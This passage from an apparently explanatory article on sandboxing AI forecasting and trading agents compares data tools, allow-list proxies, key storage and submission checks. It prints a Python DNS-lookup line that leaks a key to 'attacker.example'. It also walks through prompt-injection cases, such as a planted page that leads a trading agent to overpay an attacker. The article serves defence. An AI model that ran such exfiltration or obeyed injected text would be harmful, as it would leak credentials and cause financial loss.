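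An agent can still send information out through the arguments, though slowly. With 5,000 permitted tickers and three periods, one call can convey log₂ 15,000 ≈ 13.9 bits. An API key of 64 hexadecimal characters contains 256 bits, so an agent that had obtained one would need 19 calls to send it. An attacker would also need access to the data service's records, because only that service would receive the calls. A single free-text search query, by contrast, can hold the whole key.

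### A proxy with an allow-list

In the third design, the program fetches the prices itself, for example with `read_csv` and a web address. The sandbox's only network route leads to a proxy, a server that makes connections on the program's behalf. The program sends the proxy a hostname, such as `prices.example.com`, and the proxy opens the connection only if that name is on an allow-list.

Allowing network access only to listed hosts suits exploratory work. The model can read a data service's documentation, try a request, see the error and correct the request. Packages such as yfinance work if their hosts are on the list. The list should contain hostnames rather than IP addresses because, as Podala Narasimha points out, the IP addresses behind a hostname change.

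However, a list of approved host names is a coarse filter. Most web traffic is encrypted, so an ordinary proxy can see which host the program contacts but not the rest of the address or the data. It can't distinguish a download of prices from an upload of the host machine's secrets. If an approved site accepts uploads, a program can send files to an attacker's account there. Cloud storage is especially hard to filter this way because many customers may share one host name, and a developer who approves it for one public dataset may also approve the attacker's folder.

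An inspecting proxy can close part of this gap. It decrypts the traffic using a certificate that the sandbox trusts, so it can refuse uploads and restrict requests to particular pages. The developer has to maintain more detailed rules, and the proxy can read everything that passes through it, including any keys.

Looking up a domain name can leak information even when the proxy refuses every connection. Before a program connects to a host by name, its machine normally asks a name server for the numerical address. If the name belongs to an attacker's domain, the question eventually reaches a server that the attacker runs. A program can therefore put a secret in the name:

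```python
import socket
socket.gethostbyname("k7f29qx1.attacker.example")
```

The attacker's server receives `k7f29qx1` even if the lookup fails. Each part of a domain name can hold up to 63 characters, so a 64-character key fits in two parts of a single name. Podala Narasimha's sample policy for agents has this weakness because it limits connections to a few approved destinations but permits lookups of any domain name. Giving the sandbox no name service and letting the proxy look up only the names on its list fixes this.

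| | File from the harness | Narrow data tool | Proxy with an allow-list |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who chooses the request | The developer | The model, within checked fields | The model's program |
| What a request can carry out | Nothing from the model | A few bits per call | Anything the approved site accepts |
| Leaks through name lookups | No | No | Yes, unless only the proxy can make lookups |
| Uploads to approved sites | No | No | Yes, unless the proxy inspects traffic |
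| New data during a forecast | No | Whatever the tool covers | Anything on an approved host |

None of the three designs keeps hidden instructions out of the data.

Some developers use a code tool that the model's provider hosts, so the model's programs run on the provider's machines, away from the developer's files and keys. The provider's settings determine which of these routes exist. A developer can check which ones do by running in the hosted tool the same small test programs used on a local sandbox, including one that looks up a name on a domain the developer owns.

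### Private data, hostile text and a way out

An attacker can steal something through an agent only if the agent reads text the attacker has written, has access to something valuable, and can send it out. Podala Narasimha credits this observation to the programmer Simon Willison and to Meta, which calls its version the "Agents Rule of Two". Meta's version broadens the second condition to include access to privileged actions, and the third to include the ability to change something in the outside world. If a session lacks any one of the three, a successful prompt injection does much less damage.

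Private data is usually easier for a forecasting agent to do without than untrusted text or outbound communication. Most forecasting questions concern public events, and the harness can store API keys where the agent can't read them. The agent can't easily avoid untrusted text, because it has to read the news, and it can't avoid sending information out, because it has to search for that news and submit a forecast. An attacker who takes over such an agent can therefore still distort its forecast, but will find little private data to steal.

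This fails when the question is about private matters, such as a company's own sales next quarter. The developer can then split the work between two agents. The first reads the news, has no access to the sales records, and passes the second a single number, such as an estimate of how fast the market will grow. The second has the records but no web tools or network connection. A malicious page could make the growth estimate wrong, but it couldn't reach the sales figures, because information flows only towards the private side.

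Podala Narasimha proposes a related split for agents that manage computer clusters, in which one agent reads untrusted text and another plans privileged actions. He reports no measurements of how well it works. A drawback of limiting the message to one number is that the second agent can't see why the first expects the market to grow.

### How Metaculus bots store their keys

Metaculus's tournaments show how most independent developers handle credentials. According to Metaculus, a developer enters by creating an account for the bot, copying its access token (a password for programs) and building on a template. The quickest way is to copy the template's code on GitHub, save the keys there as encrypted "repository secrets", and have GitHub's servers run the bot on a schedule.

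The bot receives these keys as environment variables, so a code tool that ran the model's programs directly on the same machine would expose every key. Google Colab notebooks, for which Metaculus offered templates in 2024, need the same caution. The developer enters the keys in the notebook's key store and grants the notebook access, so any code that runs in the notebook may be able to read them.

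The developer can limit what an attacker could steal. In October 2024, the templates reached language models through Metaculus's own proxy, so entrants needed no keys from OpenAI or Anthropic, and each new account came with an allowance of 100,000 tokens, according to Metaculus' *Instructions Resources for Bot Building*. Someone who broke into a bot that used only this proxy would have found no OpenAI key to run up charges on. One entrant, Sygnito (2026), in *Running a Metaculus Forecasting Bot in an Isolated Lane*, keeps the bot apart from other AI systems and rotates its keys, replacing each key with a new one and cancelling the old one so that a stolen copy stops working.

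An agent should use a read-only data key if the service offers one. Otherwise, the harness has to keep reading and writing separate. The *Metaculus MCP Server* (2026), an independent project, gives an agent tools for browsing questions and for submitting or withdrawing forecasts, all using the same token. A cautious developer would switch off the tools for submitting and withdrawing while the agent researches, because a hidden instruction in an article could otherwise make it withdraw its forecasts on other questions.

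### Submission without human approval

Podala Narasimha recommends that a person approve risky actions. This would be a sensible precaution for an important forecast, but Metaculus's bot tournaments prohibit it. The first basic rule of the spring 2026 *AI Forecasting Benchmark Series* is "No human in the loop". Under the 2024 rules, a person could start the bot each day, but the bot had to submit its own forecasts, and its owner's opinion on a question could not influence them.

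Those rules don't explicitly cover approval steps. But someone who reads each probability and blocks the ones that look wrong is influencing the forecasts, so such a step would almost certainly break the rules. A person could probably still shut down a malfunctioning bot, since that doesn't favour one answer over another. The rules for human competitors are different. Metaculus says they may use AI tools as long as the final submission reflects their own decision, so a person can review an agent's work and submit it as their own forecast.

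Software has to check a bot's submissions. The harness can offer a separate submission tool that accepts only a question number and a forecast. Before sending the forecast, the tool confirms that the question is open and belongs to the right tournament. It can also rerun the agent if a probability has jumped since the previous day, for example from 20% to 95%. In 2024, only the forecast in place when a question closed counted, so a bot had up to 24 hours to correct a mistake.

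The site that receives the forecasts can also enforce limits. Metaculus represents a numerical forecast as a curve of 201 points, and for the spring 2026 season it announced that the probability between two neighbouring points could be at most 0.2, down from 0.59. Once its servers enforce this, a faulty program can't submit a forecast that puts half its probability between two neighbouring points, even if the bot's developer forgot to check for that. *Announcing Metaculus Summer 2026 FutureEval Bot Tournament* (2026) describes a testing area with one question of every type, where developers can try out the submission step.

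Each forecast must also come with a comment explaining the bot's reasoning. In 2024 Metaculus published these comments after the questions closed. If a key has entered the context, the model may also leak it by copying it into the comment, which anyone can read a day later. The harness can search comments for its own keys, but as with printed output, keeping the keys out of the context is more reliable.

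### Trading with real money

*Prediction Arena* (Zhang, Liu and colleagues, 2026) gave six language models $10,000 each to trade on the prediction market Kalshi for 57 days in early 2026. Every 15 to 45 minutes, the harness fetched prices and the agent's current holdings and passed them to the model. The model could search the web, keep notes and request trades. The harness checked each order before sending it to the exchange.

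The agents had no shell or file access and couldn't contact the exchange directly. Because they couldn't run programs, they couldn't use one to steal a trading key and get around an order limit. A developer who adds Python can keep the same protection by running it offline and leaving the trading key in the harness.

Zhang and colleagues set these limits on every account:

- An agent could spend at most 15% of its account's value on any one market.
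- The harness rejected orders that the account couldn't pay for, including fees.
- Agents couldn't borrow, or move money between accounts.
- After every cycle, the harness compared its records with the exchange's.

People monitored the agents but were not allowed to override individual trades. All six agents lost money on Kalshi, between 16.0% and 30.8% of their starting capital. The limits still worked as intended, because they were meant to cap the loss from one bad trade, not to make trades profitable. Seven positions at the 15% limit are enough to commit a whole account, so the fixed sum of $10,000 was the only firm ceiling on total losses.

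Zhang and colleagues acknowledge that a cap can hold back a good forecaster. In their example, the market prices an event at 60 cents when its true probability is 90%. The Kelly criterion, a standard formula for maximising long-run growth, sets the stake at (p − c)/(1 − c) of the account for a contract that costs c and pays $1 with probability p. Here that is 0.3/0.4, or 75%, five times the limit.

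But the formula assumes the forecast is right. If the market's 60% is right instead, repeatedly betting 75% of the account shrinks it by about 27% per bet in the long run, while betting 15% shrinks it by less than 1%. Given the losses in this experiment, the lower limit seems well worth the missed gains.

An attacker can also profit without breaking any of these limits. For example, a trader might buy 2,500 contracts at their true value of 20 cents each, plant a page that persuades an agent the event is nearly certain, and then offer the contracts at 60 cents. If the agent buys them all, it spends $1,500, exactly 15% of its account, and the trader makes $1,000. The trade passes every check on Zhang and colleagues' list. A rule against paying far more than the recent market price would block it, but would also block some good trades after real news.

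These agents read untrusted text and could trade without anyone's approval, so they had all three properties in Meta's rule. Zhang and colleagues relied on limits instead of removing one of these properties. They argue that the agents' positions were too small to affect market prices. This is doubtful for quiet markets, because they also report that live orders often failed when nobody was offering to trade at the agent's price.

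### Sources that nobody foresaw

The best argument for broader access is that developers can't predict which sources a forecasting question will need. The decisive evidence might be a port authority's table of ship arrivals or a regional health office's dashboard, and no developer would have built a tool for either or put it on an allow-list. An agent with an open connection could find such a source, write a program to read it and use figures that other forecasters had missed.

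Zhang and colleagues found no clear relationship between how much research an agent did and its returns, but they tested only six models, which is too few to settle the question.

The agent can also use the ship table without an open sandbox. It finds the table's address through a search and passes the address to a page-fetching tool. The harness downloads the table without sending any credentials and saves it as a file, which the agent's offline program reads. The agent can choose almost any public page to fetch this way.

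The address the agent requests can still carry information to the site's operator. If neither the context nor the sandbox contains anything private, the operator learns little more than what the agent is working on. That may be acceptable for a tournament bot but not for a trader, who has reason to keep the next order secret.

A fetching tool handles some sources badly, such as sites that require a login or a long series of dependent requests. The harness can record the agent's failed requests to these sources, and the developer can build a tool for the ones that recur. Metaculus's 2024 rules allowed developers to improve their bots during a tournament, but not in response to a preview of the bot's forecasts on questions that were open or about to open. A developer following those rules would therefore work from the records of closed questions.
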